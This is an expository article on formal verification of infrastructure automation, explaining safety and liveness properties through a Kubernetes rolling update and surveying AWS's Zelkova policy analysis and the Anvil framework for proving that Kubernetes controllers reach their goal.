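# Formal verification of infrastructure automation, and its limits when a learned model makes some of the decisions

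## What infrastructure automation does and what a proof about it states

Infrastructure automation is software that creates, configures, scales, repairs or removes servers, networks, storage and permissions without a person doing each step. Most large computer systems now depend on it, and a fault in it can take down thousands of services. Formal verification uses mathematical proof, or an automatic search thorough enough to count as one, to establish that a system meets a precise statement of what it must do. According to *How Amazon Web Services Uses Formal Methods* (2015), engineers at the cloud provider have used such methods on critical systems since 2011. The programs they checked followed rules that people had written, but neural networks and language models now make some of the decisions in infrastructure automation, which changes what a proof can cover.

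### Desired state and the controller loop

Suppose an engineer needs a private network with two subnets, a virtual machine in one and a gateway in the other. *Unearthing Semantic Checks for Cloud Infrastructure-as-Code Programs* (Qiu, Kon and colleagues, 2024) opens with this example. The engineer could request each piece through the cloud provider's programming interface, in the right order, keeping track of what already exists. With infrastructure as code, the engineer instead writes a text file that describes the finished network, and a tool such as Terraform works out the requests and sends them. This description, which contains no steps, is called the desired state.

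Terraform acts only when someone runs it, while a controller runs continuously. It repeatedly compares the current state with the desired state and acts to close the gap. The Kubernetes documentation page *Controllers* compares a controller to a thermostat. The dial setting is the desired state, the room temperature is the current state, and the thermostat switches the heating on or off to bring the two together. Kubernetes, an open-source system that runs applications on a cluster of machines, consists largely of controllers, each with a narrow job. One keeps the right number of copies of an application running, another assigns copies to machines, and another adds machines when the load rises. *Mutiny! How does Kubernetes fail, and what can we do about it?* (2024) explains that controllers recover easily after a restart because they act on the states they observe and have no list of commands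 to replay.

### A rolling update of three replicas

A small example introduces most of the vocabulary. The Kubernetes documentation page *Deployments* includes a file that requests three replicas (identical running copies) of the web server nginx. Its line "maxUnavailable: 1" allows at most one replica to be unavailable during an update, so at least two must stay available. An engineer changes the version number in the file from 1.14.2 to 1.16.1, and the controller gradually replaces the old replicas, a process called a rolling update. For simplicity, we assume that the cluster has no room for a fourth replica.

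Three numbers describe the state of the update: *o*, the old replicas still available; *s*, the new replicas that have started but cannot serve users yet; and *n*, the new replicas available. The controller follows two rules. It stops an old replica only when three replicas are available, and it starts a new one only when fewer than three exist. New replicas become available in their own time. Writing each state as (*o*, *s*, *n*), the update runs like this:

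(3,0,0) → (2,0,0) → (2,1,0) → (2,0,1) → (1,0,1) → (1,1,1) → (1,0,2) → (0,0,2) → (0,1,2) → (0,0,3)

A specification is a precise statement of what a system must do or never do. Here it has two parts. The first is that *o* + *n* ≥ 2 in every state the system can reach. A condition that is true in every reachable state is called an invariant. Invariants are the most common kind of safety property, which is a statement that something bad never happens. The second part is that the system eventually reaches (0,0,3), where all three replicas run the new version. This is a liveness property, a statement that something good eventually happens.

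Suppose a programmer gets the first rule slightly wrong, so that the controller counts the replicas that exist instead of those that are available. The update begins as before and reaches (2,1,0). Three replicas exist, so the controller stops another old one, and the state becomes (1,1,0). Only one replica is now available, which violates the safety property even if the new one becomes available a second later.

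A different ordering mistake breaks the liveness property. A controller with this mistake waits for a new replica to become available before it stops an old one, but it still cannot run more than three replicas at once. In the state (3,0,0), it can therefore neither stop an old replica nor start a new one. The three old replicas keep serving users and the invariant continues to hold, but the new version is never deployed. Kubernetes rejects the settings that would cause this deadlock by not allowing the number of replicas that may be unavailable and the number of extra replicas to both be zero.

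The exact definitions come from Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*. They treat an execution as an infinite sequence of states (a program that halts repeats its last state forever) and a property as a set of executions. A program has the property if all its executions lie in the set. Then:

- *P* is a safety property if every execution outside *P* has a finite beginning that no continuation can bring back into *P*.
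- *P* is a liveness property if every finite beginning whatsoever has some continuation that lies in *P*.

The sequence (3,0,0), (2,0,0), (2,1,0), (1,1,0) violates the safety property, whatever follows it. No finite record can show that the liveness property has been violated, because an update that has made no progress for an hour might still finish. Operators therefore set a deadline. By default, Kubernetes reports a rollout as stalled after 600 seconds without progress, according to Kubernetes' *Update a Deployment Without Downtime*. A deadline replaces "eventually" with "within ten minutes", which is a safety property that a monitor can check. Alpern and Schneider also proved that every property is the intersection of one safety property and one liveness property, so an engineer who has dealt with both kinds has in principle left nothing out.

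### Model checking, SMT solving and deductive proof

*Introduction to model checking* (Clarke, Henzinger and Veith, 2018) defines model checking as a computer-assisted method for analysing systems that can be described by state transitions. The tool starts from the initial state, takes every step the model permits, and continues from each new state until no new ones appear. For the correct update, it visits ten states and stops. For the controller that miscounts, it reaches (1,1,0) and prints the path there. This path is a counterexample, a concrete sequence of steps that breaks the property. A counterexample to a liveness property has to show a dead end or a loop in which the system can remain forever. *Kivi* (Liu, Lim and colleagues, 2024) applied the technique to Kubernetes. The Kivi tool takes a cluster's configuration, the properties its operator wants and assumptions about events such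 as machine failures, and returns a numbered list of steps. The paper's sample list ends at step 21 with too few replicas. Such paths can be too long to guess. At Amazon, a model checker found a possible loss of data in the design of the DynamoDB database that reviews and testing had missed, and the shortest path to it had 35 steps. The method's weakness is that the number of states grows explosively with the size of the system. When Liu and colleagues tried to check moderately large clusters directly, of 50 machines or fewer, the search ran past 10,000 seconds. They search small clusters first and stop at a size that experience suggests is enough, since every failure in their collection could occur with at most three machines and six replicas. This is good evidence about larger clusters but, as they acknowledge, not proof.

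An SMT (satisfiability modulo theories) solver is a program that checks whether a logical formula over numbers, strings and similar data can be made true. For verification, an engineer writes a formula that describes a violation, and the solver looks for values that satisfy it. For the miscounting controller, the formula combines three conditions: at least two replicas are available before the step (*o* + *n* ≥ 2), at least three exist (*o* + *s* + *n* ≥ 3), and fewer than two are available after the controller stops an old one (*o* − 1 + *n* < 2). The solver returns *o* = 2, *s* = 1, *n* = 0, which is the faulty state found above. With the correct rule, the second condition becomes *o* + *n* ≥ 3, no values satisfy all three conditions, and the solver returns "unsatisfiable". This result covers all whole numbers at once, whereas a model checker would have to go through states one by one.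 The values a solver finds may describe a state that the system never reaches, in which case the engineer has to add a condition that excludes it and run the solver again. On hard formulas, the solver may run out of time or stop without an answer, and the engineer then doesn't learn whether a violation is possible.

In a deductive proof, a person or a program constructs an argument and a proof checker verifies every step. Alpern and Schneider note that safety and liveness properties need different arguments. To prove safety, one shows that the invariant is true at the start and that each possible step preserves it. In the example, starting a replica leaves *o* + *n* unchanged, a replica becoming available raises it by one, and stopping an old replica lowers it by one but happens only when the sum is three. To prove liveness, one finds a quantity that falls with every step and cannot fall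 forever. Here that quantity is the number of steps left, *o* + 6 − *s* − 2*n*, which begins at 9 and drops by exactly one each time, and some step is always possible until it reaches zero. Arguments of this form work for a thousand replicas as well as for three. People write them in systems such as Lean, a proof assistant, or Dafny, a programming language with built-in verification. Brooker and Desai point out in *Systems Correctness Practices at AWS* that SMT solvers often do the routine parts. A failed proof attempt is less informative than a failed model check, because the checker reports a step it could not justify and the engineer must work out whether the property is false or the argument is incomplete. Deductive proof takes considerable work, but Brooker and Desai recommend it for critical security boundaries, where they think it can be worthwhile.

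### The general form of a result, and where it can fail

All three methods show that, under environment assumptions *E*, the model *M* of the system satisfies the specification *φ*, written *E*, *M* ⊨ *φ*. Environment assumptions are conditions outside the verified part that the proof relies on. A proof about the rolling update needs at least two. The first is that no replica crashes during the update, because a crash in the state (2,0,0) leaves one replica available even if the controller works correctly. The second is that every new replica eventually becomes available. In an example from the Kubernetes documentation, this assumption fails because the engineer types the version as 1.161 instead of 1.16.1. The cluster repeatedly tries to fetch software that does not exist, and the update hangs.

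It is good practice to write such assumptions down. *How Amazon Web Services Uses Formal Methods* reports that specifications at Amazon included statements as basic as "a process that has not restarted still has its local state". A recent example is *KUBEDIRECT* (2026), which describes a cluster manager that its designers checked with the specification language TLA+. Their guarantee that the cluster eventually runs the desired number of replicas assumes that the chain of controllers is fully connected infinitely often, each time for long enough to pass a round of messages from end to end. They argue that this is reasonable because a message takes only milliseconds. That may be true, but it is a claim about networks that depends on measurement, and the proof does not support it.

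A system with a correct proof can therefore still misbehave for three reasons: the specification may be wrong, the model may not match the running code, or the assumptions may not hold.

The specification may omit what people care about. In the rolling update, the guarantee depends on how "available" is defined. By default, Kubernetes counts a replica as available as soon as it is ready, so the controller can replace old replicas with a new version that crashes after ten seconds. Some failures are hard to specify at all. For example, a brief slowdown can make clients time out and retry, which adds load and prolongs the slowdown. The system does nothing forbidden and eventually makes progress, but it is down for its users. Brooker and Desai count such failures, in which a system cannot recover without intervention, among the most important causes of cloud unavailability, and note that they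 do not fit neatly under safety or liveness. Amazon's engineers use simulation for these failures.

The model may differ from the code. Liu and colleagues wrote their models of the Kubernetes controllers by hand, mostly from the source code, and simplified them. For example, the modeled controllers trigger one another directly, while the real ones communicate through a central server. They compared the model with real clusters and found close agreement, but a later release of Kubernetes could make the model inaccurate. One remedy is to check the logs of the running system against the specification, which Amazon has done since 2023 with a tool named PObserve. Another is to prove properties of the code itself. Even then, the proof assumes that some unproved code and tools are correct. This trusted base typically includes the compiler and the proof checker.

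The assumptions behind a proof may be false. For example, controllers often read the state of the cluster from a copy that can lag behind. In *Sieve*, Sun, Luo and colleagues (2024) tested ten widely used Kubernetes controllers by feeding them outdated or incomplete views and crashing them midway, and found 46 new bugs, 19 of them due to outdated views. In one case, someone deletes a database cluster and creates a new one under the same name. The controller then reads an old record that marks the first cluster for deletion, and it destroys the second along with its data. A proof that assumed current information would have been valid for that controller but would have missed the bug. Infrastructure as code has a similar problem, because the cloud provider enforces rules that the tool does not check. Microsoft's Azure cloud requires a virtual machine and its network card to be in the same region.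 Qiu and colleagues show a Terraform program that breaks this rule and passes compilation, but fails when someone deploys it.

### Three ways in which learning enters

In some systems, a small neural network makes numerical control decisions, such as how many replicas to run given the recent load. The network then replaces a written rule in the model *M*. Because it is a fixed calculation, a solver can analyze it, but the computation needed grows steeply with the network's size.

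A language model can also write the configuration, such as a Terraform file. The proof then need not cover the model, because a person or a tool can check the file before it takes effect, with the same methods used for human-written files. The open question is whether the file expresses what the person who requested it meant.

The hardest case for the methods above is an agent, a language model that chooses and carries out actions on live systems through software tools. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) keeps the classical definition, in which a plan *π* is a finite sequence of actions and verification determines whether the plan satisfies a property *φ*, written *π* ⊨ *φ*. But an agent produces its plan by a partly random process and may choose later actions only after it has the results of earlier ones, so there is often no complete plan to check beforehand.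 Researchers are therefore interested in runtime enforcement, which checks each action just before it takes effect.

Learned behaviour is harder to specify than written rules. A programmer who writes a rule usually has a reason for it, and that reason can serve as the specification. Nobody chose the individual numbers inside a trained model for a reason that could be written down. Training conveys the goal through examples and scores, but these do not settle what the right behaviour is in situations unlike the examples.

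## Proving what an access policy permits: Amazon's Zelkova

Proof works best on small, fixed, precise configurations, such as access policies. An access policy lists who may do what to which resource in a cloud, such as who may read a file. Amazon Web Services (AWS) checks the relevant policies for each request, then grants or denies it. The policy language has no loops or arithmetic, so there is no sequence of states to search, but the number of possible requests is enormous. *Semantic-based Automated Reasoning for AWS Access Policies using SMT* (Backes, Bolignano and colleagues, 2018) describes Zelkova, a tool that uses SMT solvers to reason about all of these requests at once.

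### A policy as a formula

A policy consists of statements. Each has an effect (allow or deny), a principal (the user, account or service making the request), an action, a resource and sometimes conditions, such as the network the request must come from. AWS denies every request by default. An allow statement overrides this default, and a deny statement overrides any allow statement, whatever their order. A request therefore succeeds exactly when some allow statement matches it and no deny statement does:

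(*A*₁ ∨ *A*₂ ∨ …) ∧ ¬(*D*₁ ∨ *D*₂ ∨ …)

Each *A* is the formula for an allow statement, and each *D* is the formula for a deny statement. The symbols ∨, ∧ and ¬ mean "or", "and" and "not". A statement matches when it lists the request's principal, action and resource, and all its conditions hold.

Zelkova's basic operation compares two policies. Policy *X* is no more permissive than policy *Y* if *Y* allows every request that *X* allows. In logical terms, *X* implies *Y* (*X* ⇒ *Y*) for every request. A solver can check this by looking for a request that *X* allows and *Y* does not (*X* ∧ ¬*Y*). If no such request exists, the implication is valid.

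### The exam files

Backes and colleagues illustrate the comparison with a university course, cs240, that keeps its files in Amazon's S3 storage service. Policy *X* lets students read the exam and lets teaching assistants ("tas") read both the exam and the answers. Policy *Y* lets everyone read everything in the course folder, except that students may not read the answers. In the formulas, *p*, *a* and *r* stand for the principal, action and resource of an arbitrary request, getObject is the action that reads a file, and the star matches any text.

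| Statement | Formula |
|---|---|
| *X*₀: allow students to read the exam | *a* = getObject ∧ *p* = students ∧ *r* = cs240/Exam.pdf |
| *X*₁: allow assistants to read the exam and the answers | *a* = getObject ∧ *p* = tas ∧ (*r* = cs240/Exam.pdf ∨ *r* = cs240/Answer.pdf) |
| *Y*₀: allow everyone to read everything | *a* = getObject ∧ *r* matches `cs240/*` |
| *Y*₁: deny students the answers | *a* = getObject ∧ *p* = students ∧ *r* = cs240/Answer.pdf |

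Policy *X* has two allow statements, so its formula is *X*₀ ∨ *X*₁. Policy *Y* has one allow and one deny statement, so its formula is *Y*₀ ∧ ¬*Y*₁.

In this example, one can prove by hand that the implication *X* ⇒ *Y* is valid. Any request that *X* allows satisfies *X*₀ or *X*₁. If it satisfies *X*₀, a student is reading the exam. The exam is in the folder, so *Y*₀ is true, and the exam is not the answer file, so *Y*₁ is false. If the request satisfies *X*₁, the file is again in the folder, so *Y*₀ is true, and *Y*₁ is false because the principal is not "students". Policy *Y* therefore allows the request in both cases.

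The reverse implication fails. Policy *Y* also lets students read any other file in the folder, such as ClassRoster.pdf. Worse, its deny statement applies only to the principal "students", so anyone else in the world can read the whole folder, including the answers. Whoever wrote *Y* presumably wanted to protect the answers, and the policy appears to do so, but a student could read them by using a different account.

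The same comparison can check an organisation's own rules, because they can be written as policies. Suppose the university wants nobody to read course files from outside its own network. An administrator writes a policy that allows getObject only from that network and allows all other actions from anywhere. This policy is an upper bound, and a course policy obeys the rule if it implies the bound. Policy *Y* breaks the rule because it has no condition on the network. With a lower bound, the required permissions must imply the policy. Amazon's threat detection service GuardDuty uses Zelkova to check a lower bound, so that it knows new customers have given it the permissions it needs.

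### Scanning the text and testing single requests

Before Zelkova, some AWS customers scanned their policies for suspicious text, such as a wildcard in place of the principal. A scan would flag policy *Y*, but scans can also flag safe policies and miss unsafe ones. AWS's *Understanding S3 Block Public Access* gives an example of a false alarm. The policy's first statement uses a wildcard to let everybody read the files, but its second denies access to everyone outside one organisation.

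A scan can also miss a policy that grants public access. Backes and colleagues compare two policies for a message queue, both of which let anyone send a message, subject to a condition that names the source "mytopic". The first policy uses the operator ArnEquals. The second uses ForAllValues:ArnEquals, which changes the condition to "if the request names a source, then the source is mytopic". A request that names no source satisfies this, so anyone can send messages to the queue. The difference is clear in the formula, but a scanner that looks for wildcards without conditions would pass both policies.

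AWS lets users submit a specific request and see the decision, which is reliable for that request only. Someone who tests policy *Y* by requesting the answer file as a student and then as a teaching assistant gets the expected result both times, and has no particular reason to try a stranger.

### Wildcards, speed and scale

Wildcards cause most of the computational difficulty. They make the problem PSPACE-complete, meaning it is among the hardest problems solvable with memory that grows only polynomially with the size of the input. No known algorithm solves every instance quickly.

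Wildcards also make it easy to write a wrong formula. The pattern `ab*bc` matches any text that begins with "ab" and ends with "bc", except "abc", whose single "b" would have to count twice. Zelkova's formula excludes this case explicitly. Patterns with more than two stars need regular expressions, a more general notation for text patterns, and the standard solvers sometimes failed on these. For example, neither Z3 nor CVC4 could prove that every text that matches `ab*b*b*b` also matches `a*b*b*b`. Amazon's engineers therefore built an extension of Z3 that converts each pattern into a finite automaton, a simple machine that reads text one character at a time. Zelkova runs the solvers in parallel and uses the first answer.

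Real policies are much easier to check than the worst case. In 2018, Zelkova answered 99% of a million randomly selected queries within 160 milliseconds. If it cannot handle part of a policy, or if the solvers run out of time, it returns "unknown", and the calling service needs a default. S3 treats a policy as public when the check times out. This protects the data, but it can lock legitimate users out of files even when nobody has changed the policy.

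In 2018, AWS services called Zelkova between a few million and tens of millions of times a day. According to Amazon Science's *How academic collaboration delivers real-world security to Amazon customers*, the newer solver cvc5 now handles about a billion calls a day across AWS. That figure is larger than the number of policy checks because it includes calls from other products, such as one that checks written text against an organisation's rules, and because a single question about a policy can require several solver calls.

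Amazon Science's *A decade of mathematical certainty* names two prominent uses of Zelkova: S3 Block Public Access and IAM Access Analyzer. Block Public Access rejects any policy that would open a bucket, S3's unit of storage, to the public, and AWS has switched it on for all new buckets since April 2023. Access Analyzer includes checks that a company can run before deploying a policy. AWS's *IAM Access Analyzer custom policy checks* describes one that determines whether an edited policy grants new access by testing whether the new version logically implies the old one. Amazon also applies automated reasoning to policies that limit AI agents, and the newer policy language Cedar is important for this use.

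### Asking who has access

An implication check compares a policy with a bound, and few customers can write a suitable one. They would have to know which property matters, express it precisely and interpret the result. *Stratified Abstraction of Access Control Policies* (Backes, Berrueco and colleagues, 2020) describes a method that avoids this by answering "who has access?" instead of "is this policy correct?" The method runs inside IAM (Identity and Access Management) Access Analyzer, which AWS launched in December 2019. The tool produces a short list of findings, and the customer decides whether each one describes intended access.

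Their example is a policy with three statements:

- Allow requests from the network vpc-a or the network vpc-b.
- Allow requests from the organisation o-2.
- Deny requests from vpc-b unless they come from the organisation o-1.

Listing every request that this policy allows is hopeless, since there are 10¹² possible AWS account numbers and 2¹²⁸ possible addresses in the newer internet address format alone. But the policy mentions only two networks and two organisations and treats all others alike, so nine groups cover every request:

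| | o-1 | o-2 | Any other organisation |
|---|---|---|---|
| vpc-a | allowed | allowed | allowed |
| vpc-b | allowed | denied | denied |
| Any other network | denied | allowed | denied |

The algorithm begins with the broadest description, "anyone", and narrows it only where necessary, because five separate findings, one for each allowed group, would be accurate but repetitive, and real policies have many more fields. It uses Zelkova to check whether the policy allows a request that no narrower description covers, which here means one from an unlisted network and an unlisted organisation. The policy denies such requests, so "anyone" is too broad.

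The algorithm then tries the four descriptions that fix one field. It keeps "vpc-a", because the policy allows requests from vpc-a even when they come from an unlisted organisation. It keeps "o-2" for a similar reason, and rejects "vpc-b" and "o-1". The only combination that the accepted descriptions do not already cover is vpc-b together with o-1, and the policy allows it. After six questions to Zelkova, the customer gets three findings:

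- The network is vpc-a.
- The organisation is o-2.
- The network is vpc-b and the organisation is o-1.

Backes, Berrueco and colleagues prove that the findings cover every request the policy allows, so a customer who approves all of them has approved everything the policy permits. However, a finding can be slightly too broad. The second one includes requests from o-2 through vpc-b, which the policy denies. This might cause a false alarm, but no permitted access goes unreported.

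The method was tested on 165 policies, which were the ones complex enough to be interesting among 1,387 drawn at random from those in use. The tool took less than 430 milliseconds per finding on all but one of them. The evaluation covers speed and brevity, but not whether customers judge the findings correctly. This matters a great deal because their judgement now takes the place of a written specification. If someone approves a dangerous finding by mistake, the tool cannot detect the mistake.

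### Deciding what "public" means

Customers don't give Block Public Access a specification, so Amazon had to write one. *Block Public Access* (2020) introduces a formal notion, trust safety, which a policy satisfies if it gives access only to trusted principals. The tool has to infer from the policy whom the customer trusts. AWS explains that the tool accepts limits based on something a particular party owns and controls, such as an account number, but not limits based on a first name, because nobody controls who has that name.

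Under this definition, a policy that admits everyone in one organisation is not public, even if the organisation has hundreds of thousands of users. Zelkova classifies another of AWS's examples as public, although it looks much stricter. The user must be called Alice, carry the tag "finance", belong to some organisation, use two-factor authentication and a secure connection, and come from the private network address 10.20.30.40. The policy is still public because a stranger could arrange all of these things in an account of their own.

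D'Antoni, Gacek and colleagues (2024), in *Projective model counting for IP addresses in access control policies*, explain that Zelkova also treats a policy as public if the number of internet addresses it admits exceeds a threshold. They expressed this count in a form that ordinary solvers can handle, and their check takes less than three seconds for 99.999% of the policies they evaluated. The solver can prove that a policy stays under the threshold, but people at Amazon had to choose the threshold, and no proof can show that they chose well. "Not public" is also a weak guarantee, because a policy that lets every employee read the payroll would pass.

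Researchers outside Amazon have worked on measuring how permissive a policy is, which gives more information than a yes-or-no answer. *Neurosymbolic Characterization for Reliable Access Control Policy Analysis* (2025) applies such measurements to policies written by language models.

### Combinations of policies and the engine itself

A result about the formula is useful only if the formula matches how AWS makes its access decisions. The authorization engine, the program that makes these decisions, often has to combine several policies. *Modeling the AWS Authorization Engine* (Barnett, D'Antoni and colleagues, 2025) shows that separate results for each policy are not enough. In its example, Ace, a role (an identity that a person or program can assume) in account 111, can read Photo, a bucket in account 222, only if both accounts permit it.

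Suppose Ace's own policy allows the request. If the bucket has no policy, the engine denies the request. If the bucket has a policy that grants access to account 111 without mentioning Ace, the engine allows the request, because account 222 has delegated the decision to account 111, which has approved Ace. But if Zelkova examines each policy separately with Ace as the principal, it finds both times that Ace's policy allows the request and the bucket's does not, so no rule for combining those two results can give the right answer in both cases.

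Barnett and colleagues solve this by also evaluating the bucket's policy with account 111 as the principal instead of Ace. If no deny statement applies, the engine grants access when Ace's policy allows the request and the bucket's policy allows either Ace or the account. Their tool builds such combinations for the various policy types and gives the resulting formula to the solvers. It answers 99% of requests within 349 milliseconds. One team at Amazon uses it to check proposed organisation-wide policies for access that should never be possible and for restrictions that would break applications. AWS now offers customers a version of Access Analyzer that evaluates several policies together.

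To test whether their model matched the engine, Barnett and colleagues generated about 1,500 cases covering the ways policies of different types can interact. The model and the engine agreed on all of them. A third program, which they wrote from the public documentation, missed two edge cases, and Amazon corrected the documentation. These tests are good evidence but not a proof, and they rely on Zelkova interpreting each individual policy correctly.

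Another group at Amazon proved properties of the engine's code. *Formally Verified Cloud-Scale Authorization* (Chakarov, Geldenhuys et al., 2025) describes the group's four-year project to replace the old engine, a Java program that handled a billion requests per second. The group first wrote a simple specification in Dafny and proved 52 properties of it, including that a deny statement always overrides an allow statement. They then wrote a faster implementation, proved that it always gives the same result as the specification, and translated it into Java. The specification of wildcard matching, for example, is only a few lines long but can take exponential time to run. The faster version is 220 lines long, and about half of those lines exist only for the proof.

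The proof could not show that the specification matched the old engine, which customers relied on. Early tests revealed 13 differences. In 2023, the team ran both engines on live requests and found seven more differences, all caused by errors or gaps in the specification. In one case, the team had left milliseconds out of dates and times to simplify the proofs, reasoning that policy changes take seconds to spread through the cloud anyway. The old engine used milliseconds, so the two engines reached different decisions on some real requests. The final version agreed with the old engine on 10¹⁵ requests and was about three times as fast. Amazon deployed it in 2024.

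The new engine still has a trusted base, which includes the Dafny verifier, roughly 1,500 lines of assumptions about Java's standard library, and the team's own translator from Dafny to Java. The team tested the translator with randomly generated programs, which exposed several bugs, but did not prove it correct. They also kept the Java output readable so that engineers who didn't know Dafny could review it.

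### Later edits, information flow and time

Each Zelkova result applies only to the version of the policy it checked. If someone adds a statement, the result may no longer hold, so Access Analyzer runs again after each change. *Verification of Robust Properties for Access Control Policies* (2026) proposes an alternative for policies that are still incomplete. Its method proves only properties that will hold however the policy is later extended, so they don't need to be checked again.

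The formula also covers only the decision to grant access, not what happens to the data afterwards. Suppose Alice may read a secret file and write to a shared folder, and Bob may read the folder but not the file. Each permission may be what its author intended, yet Alice can copy the secret into the shared folder, where Bob can read it. *Checking Information Flow in Cloud-based IoT Access Control Policies (Extended Version)* (2026) addresses this problem in access policies for networks of connected devices, and reports finding no earlier work that verified information flow in such policies.

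Finally, the formula does not represent time. Zelkova can use it to prove that a policy gives a contractor no access today, but not that the software managing the contractor's temporary permission will eventually revoke it. Eventual revocation is a liveness property of a running controller, and proving it requires a model of how the controller behaves over time.

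## Proving that a Kubernetes controller reaches its goal: Anvil

A controller exists to bring something about, so proving only a safety property is of limited use. A controller that never did anything would usually satisfy that property. Sun, Ma and colleagues (2024) proved a liveness property for three Kubernetes controllers using Anvil, their framework for writing controllers in Rust together with machine-checked proofs about the code.

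### A crash between two steps

Their opening example is a controller that sets up ZooKeeper, a service that distributed programs use to coordinate with one another. The controller has to create three objects in the cluster's data store: a network service, a configuration map that holds ZooKeeper's settings, and a stateful set, which causes Kubernetes to start three servers. In outline, the code is:

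```
if the service does not exist:
    create the service
    create the configuration map
create the stateful set
```

If the controller crashes just after it creates the service, Kubernetes restarts it, and it runs the procedure from the top. The service now exists, so the controller skips both indented lines and goes straight to the stateful set. It will never create the configuration map, however often it runs. Real controllers often have bugs of this kind, and tests tend to miss them because the crash has to happen between two particular steps.

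A safety property such as "the cluster never enters an intermediate state from which the controller cannot recover" could exclude the bug. But to write it precisely, an engineer would have to know which states those are, which is almost the same as already knowing the bug. With a liveness property, the engineer only has to describe the goal.

### Eventually stable reconciliation

Sun, Ma and colleagues call their property eventually stable reconciliation (ESR). If the desired state stops changing, the cluster eventually matches it and keeps matching it from then on. As a formula:

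∀*d*. □(□desire(*d*) ⇒ ◇□match(*d*))

Here *d* is a description of a desired state, desire(*d*) means that *d* is the current description, and match(*d*) means that the cluster matches it. The box □ means "now and at all later times", and the diamond ◇ means "now or at some later time". The formula is easiest to read from the inside out:

- ◇□match(*d*) combines progress and stability. At some point the cluster matches the description, and after that it never stops matching it.
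- □desire(*d*) is the condition for this promise. If users kept editing the description forever, the controller would be chasing a moving target.
- The outer □ makes the promise apply from every moment of an execution, including the moment after a crash has left the work half done.
- ∀*d* extends it to every description that a user could write.

The ZooKeeper bug violates progress. A controller that reaches the goal and later undoes its own work violates stability.

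The formula guarantees only that the controller will reach the desired state set by the last edit. A controller can't detect which edit is the last, so in practice it must reach any desired state that stays unchanged for long enough. The formula sets no limit on how long that can be, so a controller that took a year would satisfy it.

ESR also doesn't restrict how the controller reaches its goal. In the rolling update described earlier, a controller could satisfy ESR by stopping all three old replicas at once and then starting three new ones, but the website would be down in the meantime. The requirement that at least two replicas stay available is a separate safety property and needs its own proof.

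ESR still rules out a large share of known bugs. Two testing tools had found bugs in 16 popular controllers, and 70 of those bugs (69%) left the controller unable to reach the desired state.

### Connecting the Rust code to a model

A developer who uses Anvil writes the controller as a state machine. Its central function, `step`, takes the desired state, the response to the previous request, and the controller's internal state. It returns the next internal state and at most one new request. This limit simplifies the proof, because nothing else can change the cluster halfway through a step.

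The developer then writes a model, which is a second, more abstract version of the state machine. Verus, a Rust verification tool that uses the SMT solver Z3, checks that the code and the model give the same output for every input. This check catches any mismatch between the two, which could go unnoticed if nobody checked the model against the code.

Anvil supplies a model of everything around the controller. It includes:

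- a network that may deliver messages in any order
- the API server, through which all components read and change the cluster's state, and which rejects an update based on an old version of an object
- users who may change the desired state at any time
- three of Kubernetes' built-in controllers, among them the garbage collector, which deletes objects whose owners no longer exist

At each step of the combined model, either one component acts or one fault occurs. The controller may crash any number of times, losing everything in its memory, and any request may fail. The proof has to cover every possible order of these events.

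Proving liveness also requires assuming that certain events eventually happen, since a network that held a message forever would keep any controller from reaching its goal. Anvil assumes weak fairness, which means that an action that remains possible eventually occurs. No controller could finish its work if it crashed at every step, but assuming at most one crash would make the result weak. Sun, Ma and colleagues therefore assume that any number of faults may happen but that they eventually stop. Faults in a real cluster never stop for good, so in practice the theorem implies only that the controller recovers during a sufficiently long period without faults.

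### The steps of the proof

The first half of the proof shows that the environment eventually settles. Suppose a controller requests three servers and crashes right after sending the request. The user then changes the number to five, and the restarted controller sends a new request. The old request may still be in the network, and it conflicts with the new one. The proof therefore has to show that every request based on an old description eventually leaves the network.

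The second half of the proof shows that the controller reaches its goal in a settled environment from any starting point. Earlier crashes could have left the controller at any point in its procedure. The proof avoids treating each case separately by showing that the current run of the procedure ends, that a new run starts, and that a run from the beginning creates or corrects every object.

Each of these arguments is a chain of links of the form "*P* leads to *Q*". For one link, let *P* be "a request to create the configuration map is on its way", let *Q* be "the configuration map exists", and let *A* be the action in which the API server handles the request. Then *P* leads to *Q* if four conditions hold:

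1. Whatever happens next, either *P* remains true or *Q* becomes true.
2. If *A* happens, *Q* becomes true.
3. *A* is possible whenever *P* is true.
4. *A* is subject to weak fairness.

The first three conditions concern single steps, which an SMT solver can check. Solvers have no general procedure for proving that something eventually happens, so Anvil provides more than 70 proved lemmas for combining the single-step results. For example, one lemma combines "*P* leads to *Q*" and "*Q* leads to *R*" into "*P* leads to *R*". For the faulty ZooKeeper controller, the proof fails at the state where the service exists but the configuration map does not, because no later step sends the missing request.

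### Three verified controllers

Sun, Ma and colleagues built controllers for ZooKeeper, the message broker RabbitMQ and the logging service Fluent Bit. For each, they took a widely used unverified controller as a reference. They matched all the features of the Fluent Bit reference and the key features of the other two.

| | ZooKeeper | RabbitMQ | Fluent Bit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of executable code | 1,134 | 1,598 | 1,208 |
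| Lines of proof | 8,352 | 7,228 | 8,395 |
| Lines of proof per line of code | 7.4 | 4.5 | 6.9 |
| Mean time per run, verified controller | 439 ms | 439 ms | 195 ms |
| Mean time per run, reference controller | 212 ms | 690 ms | 221 ms |

The verified ZooKeeper controller takes twice as long to run as the reference controller, which skips some unnecessary updates. The difference hardly matters, because the controller's running time is less than 1% of the time the cluster takes to reach the desired state. Most of the rest is spent on tasks such as restarting containers.

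Each controller took about two and a half person-months to write and verify. The first ESR proof, for ZooKeeper, took two person-months because the team had to work out the proof strategy. The proofs for the other two took around two person-weeks. The team later added 28 features to a basic version of the Fluent Bit controller. On average, a feature took less than a day and required changes to 47 lines, 19 of them in the proof.

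The proofs exposed four bugs in early versions of the ZooKeeper and RabbitMQ controllers. One resembled the opening example. If the ZooKeeper controller crashed partway through changing the number of servers, it could not continue after restarting. The reference ZooKeeper controller had a similar bug. Another of the four came from a naming rule copied from the reference RabbitMQ controller. The rule could give two separate RabbitMQ clusters a service with the same name, and the controller would then keep changing that service forever to suit each cluster in turn. The team found this bug because they could not prove stability.

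They also proved a safety property for RabbitMQ, that the number of replicas never decreases, because removing replicas can lose data. At first they only forbade users to lower the number in the description, but they found a gap when they tried to prove the property. If a user deletes a large cluster's description and writes a new one for a smaller cluster, the old stateful set may still exist for a while, and the controller would shrink it. The corrected controller waits for the garbage collector to delete the old stateful set.

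### What the proof takes for granted

After finishing the proofs, the team ran 993 functional tests and 854 crash tests on the three controllers. The functional tests found one bug, and the crash tests found none. The ZooKeeper controller changes the number of servers by calling ZooKeeper's own programming interface, and the proof relied on the team's description of that interface. The description left out the case in which a badly configured ZooKeeper keeps running but refuses all changes, and in that case the controller got stuck.

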